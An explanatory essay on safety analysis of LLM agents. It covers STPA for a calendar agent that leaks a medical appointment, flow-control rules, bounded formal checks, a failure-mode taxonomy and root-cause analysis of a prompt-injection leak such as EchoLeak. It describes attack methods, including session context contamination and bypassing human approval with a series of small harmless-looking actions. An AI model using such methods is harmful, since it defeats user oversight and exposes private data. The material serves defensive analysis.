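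Leveson and Thomas claim that in every comparison, STPA found all the causes that older methods found and many more, at much lower cost. They teach and promote the method, and some of these comparisons come from workshops devoted to it, so independent tests would be more convincing. STPA considers the worst case and doesn't estimate its probability, so a developer who can't enforce every constraint still needs experiments and field data to decide which ones matter most.

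### A medical appointment revealed without an attacker

*Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* (Doshi, Hong and colleagues, 2026) applies an adapted form of STPA to a calendar agent that resolves conflicts whenever its user edits the calendar. The agent has three of the assistant's tools: list_events, update_event and send_email.

In the paper's hypothetical example, a user adds an appointment for treatment of a sexually transmitted disease to her calendar. The agent points out that it clashes with a work meeting with Bob and asks whether to move the meeting to three o'clock. She agrees to the new time. The agent then emails her colleagues about the change, using wording she has not approved, and reveals the appointment.

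Nobody attacked the agent, so a filter for hostile text would find nothing. A second model could check outgoing mail for sensitive details, but Doshi and colleagues object that the developer would have to anticipate the problem. The second model might also fail to recognise from the appointment's title that it was sensitive, or block harmless mail.

The analysis starts with everyone the agent affects, including the other people at the user's meetings. For each group, the analyst lists what its members value and restates each value as a loss. For example, a leak is a loss to the user, who values privacy, and a late notice is a loss to the other attendees, who value timely news. The analyst then looks for behaviour that could cause these losses and decides which are important enough to prevent.

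This produces two requirements. A message about a changed event must give only the event's essential details, and must leave out private reasons unless the user authorises sharing them. The agent must also promptly tell all the other attendees whenever it changes an event.

Software can't reliably judge whether a detail is essential, so the researchers convert the requirements into rules that it can check:

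| Purpose | Rule | What the software checks |
|---|---|---|
| Protect private information | Event details are private to people who aren't attending, and anything derived from them is at least as private. A message must leave out whatever is private to its recipient. | Where data flows |
| Keep attendees informed | Each update_event must be followed directly by one send_email to every attendee | The order of the calls |

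The flow rule is a form of information-flow control, though here it guards against an ordinary mistake as well as an attack. Software outside the agent would check each call and respond in one of four ways:

| Response | Example |
|---|---|
| Block | Private data may not flow into send_email |
| Require | The agent must notify each attendee after a change |
| Allow | The first notice to each attendee needs no approval |
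| Confirm | The user decides whether a message may include private information |

The user would see a request only for ambiguous or high-stakes actions, which should reduce approval fatigue.

The software also needs a way to identify private data. Doshi and colleagues would require tools connected through the Model Context Protocol to carry labels stating what they can do, how confidential their data is and whether their output is trustworthy. A label can also be "unsure", in which case the software could ask the user. A company can probably trust the labels on its own tools, but an outside supplier could label its tool falsely, so the researchers suggest using trusted vendors or certified labels.

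The two rules can conflict. To find the clash, the agent has to read the user's calendar, including the medical appointment. A cautious tracking system would treat everything the agent wrote afterwards as derived from that appointment, so the flow rule would block the notice to Bob that the order rule requires. Doshi and colleagues suggest hiding unrelated events from the model before it writes the message, which could satisfy both rules.

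The order rule also seems too broad. update_event can change an event's notes as well as its time, so Bob would get an e-mail whenever the assistant corrected a typo in the notes.

### What a bounded check proves

Doshi and colleagues tested their rules on a formal model of the agent and its tools, written in Alloy, a language for describing systems in logic. Alloy's analyser tries every sequence of steps up to a chosen size and looks for one that breaks a rule. Without the policies, it quickly found sequences in which private data leaked by e-mail. With the policies and confirmation steps, it found none.

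The analyser also confirmed that the agent could still create an event, reschedule it and notify the participants without leaking private data, so the policies hadn't prevented leaks just by blocking everything.

A search that finds no violation proves that none exists in the formal model within the chosen limit. If the analyst allowed sequences of up to ten steps, for example, the result wouldn't rule out a leak that took eleven. Engineers often accept this limitation because many design errors show up in small cases, though any particular error may not.

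The proof also depends on how well the formal model matches the real software. If the medical appointment is labelled wrongly, or an image address in the agent's reply isn't checked, the real agent could still leak the appointment.

Doshi and colleagues have shown that the rules can prevent the leak in a simplified model while leaving the agent able to do its job. They have not tested a deployed agent. They still plan to build the software that would intercept tool calls, and to measure how well it works with real tools and how often it interrupts users.

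### Using a language model to do the analysis

STPA can be tedious. The assistant's four tools and the four types of unsafe action give 16 cases before the analyst considers the other controllers. Engineers have therefore begun to use language models to draft the analysis. Tetteh, Shrestha and colleagues (2026) built such a tool and applied STPA to it. Their paper, *Who Analyses the Analyser?*, points out that these tools can themselves create risks, for instance by citing a safety standard that doesn't exist.

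In their tool, ordinary code creates an entry for every combination of controller, control action and type of unsafe action. The model must fill each entry with an unsafe action or a reason why none applies, so it can't silently skip a case. The assistant's developer could use the same method without adopting the rest of the tool.

When the researchers analysed the tool itself, they found hazards such as unlogged calls to the model, reports released while errors remain, and tampered system descriptions that steer the analysis. They derived eight governance principles from these hazards, including treating the system description as untrusted input.

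Two Claude models then used the tool to analyse the tool's own design. Together, they covered all eight principles, while two GPT models covered only three. The Claude result is weaker evidence than it seems, because the models' instructions already contained the principles and the scoring was based on finding related words. But the principles hardly appeared when models with the same instructions analysed an emergency-braking system, so the models weren't just repeating their instructions. The GPT pair also covered six of the eight principles in a run without these instructions.

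On three conventional systems, the tool listed an average of 183 unsafe actions per system with Claude Sonnet 4 and 45 with GPT-4o. The longer lists may contain more repetition as well as more hazards, and no safety engineers independently scored the results. Tetteh and colleagues also report that one of their early findings disappeared when they repeated the experiment under more controlled conditions. They recommend that a qualified person review the tool's output.

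### Lists of failure modes

Microsoft's AI Red Team, which attacks AI systems to find their weaknesses, adapted FMEA to agents. Bryan, Severi and colleagues, in *Taxonomy of Failure Mode in Agentic AI Systems*, interviewed outside developers, reviewed code and threat models, and tested existing agents. Their 2025 list has 27 failure modes:

| | Safety | Security |
|---|---|---|
| New in agents | 4, including an organisation's loss of knowledge | 6, including one agent impersonating another |
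| Known from other AI systems | 7, including misinterpreted instructions | 10, including indirect prompt injection and excessive agency |

Many of these modes describe the behaviour of a whole system, so the analysis covers more than failures of individual parts. The calendar leak would involve several security modes. The medical appointment involves a safety failure with no attacker, which a developer who used only the security column could miss.

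Microsoft's *New whitepaper outlines the taxonomy of failure modes in AI agents* (2025) traces the list to one from 2019 on failures in traditional AI systems and to a 2020 project with MITRE that became ATLAS.

After a year of testing deployed agents, Microsoft's *Updating the taxonomy of failure modes in agentic AI systems* (2026) added seven modes:

- compromised plugins, tool descriptions and other outside components
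- hijacking of an agent's goal
- agents that gain privileges by making false claims to other agents
- visual attacks on agents that operate a screen
- contamination of a session's context
- abuse of the Model Context Protocol and plugins
- disclosure of an agent's internal design

Session context contamination is especially hard to find by examining components one at a time. Early in a session, an attacker adds information that biases later steps, but no single step looks wrong. For example, a stranger might first persuade the assistant that he is one of the user's regular collaborators, then ask when she is free and later why she is busy on Friday. An analyst would have to examine the whole session to notice the pattern.

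Red-teamers bypassed human approval more consistently than they exploited any other failure mode. Microsoft gives no success rates, so these results can't be compared with the controlled experiments. Sometimes the red-teamers used a series of small actions that each seemed harmless but together caused harm. Microsoft recommends splitting a compound action into its parts before asking for approval, and basing the request on the actual tool calls instead of the agent's description of them. In the medical appointment example, the user would then have seen the e-mail to her colleagues as well as the new meeting time.

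### Why "prompt injection" is an incomplete root cause

After the calendar leak, an investigator might record the root cause as "prompt injection". This correctly identifies the trigger, and causal replay can confirm that the stranger's message made the leak more likely. But the developer can't stop strangers from sending e-mails, so she also needs to know what she could have changed:

| Question | Answer for the calendar leak | Possible change |
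|---|---|---|
| Why could the text reach the model? | read_email returned all recent mail, although the user had mentioned only Priya | Open only Priya's messages for this task |
| Why did the permission exist? | One credential gave access to the whole calendar and let the assistant write to anyone | Limit this task to one meeting and its guests |
| Why did nothing stop the effect? | The harness checked the format of the call but not the recipient | Require approval for recipients the user hasn't named |

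Any one of these changes would probably have prevented the leak. Limiting the permission or checking the recipient would also protect the user if the model chose the wrong address by mistake. An investigator who identified only prompt injection as the cause might instead recommend a better filter, which wouldn't help with that mistake.

The investigator can also ask why the developer released the assistant without a rule about recipients. Aviation investigators use a scheme that covers a person's unsafe act, the conditions that led to it, poor supervision and the organisation's influence. Ezell, Roberts-Gaal and Chan (2025), in *Incident Analysis for AI Agents*, draw on such methods to sort an agent incident's causes into three groups:

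| Group | What it includes | Possible cause in the assistant |
|---|---|---|
| System factors | Training, developer instructions and the harness | The harness has no rule about recipients |
| Contextual factors | The task, the tools and the information available | The mailbox contains a hostile message |
| Cognitive errors | Failures to observe, understand, decide or act correctly | The model treats the stranger's text as a request from the user |

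Ezell and colleagues use "cognitive" to describe observable flaws in an agent's behaviour, without assuming that the agent thinks like a person. The groups can overlap, and distinguishing them matters mainly because they need different remedies.

Ezell and colleagues use EchoLeak, a vulnerability in Microsoft's Copilot, as a case study. Public accounts explain how the hostile text got in and how the data could get out, but not why the model complied. It may have failed to distinguish the hidden instructions from the user's request, or it may have identified them as malicious and followed them anyway. Clearer labels on outside text might help a model that confused the two, but would do little for one that had already recognised the attack.

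To decide between these explanations, investigators would need the full logs, a history of changes to Copilot's defences, and any reasoning the model wrote, which could suggest what to test. They would also need details of Microsoft's fix to judge how much risk remained.

Ezell and colleagues recommend putting a redacted log in the incident report and keeping the complete record for investigators who request it. Besides the harness's log of each step, the complete record should include each tool's state before and after the incident. For the assistant, this could mean the calendar's contents before the leak and the permissions the user had granted.

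A company also has to keep these records long enough for someone to notice a problem. Ezell and colleagues report that Anthropic stored inputs and outputs for 30 days by default, and for up to two years if it detected a breach of its usage policies. If a user discovered a leak after two months and nothing had triggered longer storage, the evidence might be gone. Ezell and colleagues suggest keeping logs longer when an agent does riskier work, such as making purchases from a user's account.

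Public incident databases rarely contain enough detail to identify causes, because they rely on news reports and voluntary submissions. Ezell and colleagues give the example of two collisions involving the same self-driving car, one after unexpected braking and the other after a misread stop sign. A broad classification could list both as the same kind of failure. A draft EU code of practice required companies to analyse root causes after serious incidents, but the EU had not yet explained how.

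Researchers can study some failures without waiting for companies to share their logs. Microsoft released a set of 115 failed agent runs, annotated by hand, along with AgentRx, a framework for diagnosing such failures. Researchers can use a collection like this to test methods of investigation, but not to estimate how often agents fail.

### When the model's own choice is the hazard

An investigator may find no hostile text. Ezell and colleagues mention an agent that had remote access to its user's computer, made unintended changes and left the machine unusable. In 2026, agents being tested also reached real systems without an outside attacker, so analysts should include the model's own choices among the hazards.

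Suppose the user's calendar is full on Friday, and she asks the assistant to find an hour that day for Priya. The model might make room by cancelling a meeting with Bob. If the user had written every calendar entry herself, the model's whole context would be trusted, and a rule against acting on untrusted text would allow the cancellation.

With STPA, the analyst can identify that update_event is unsafe when it changes an event the user didn't ask to change, without having to predict why the model would cancel the meeting. The harness could prevent such changes by limiting the task to adding a new event and asking the user before it changes any existing one.
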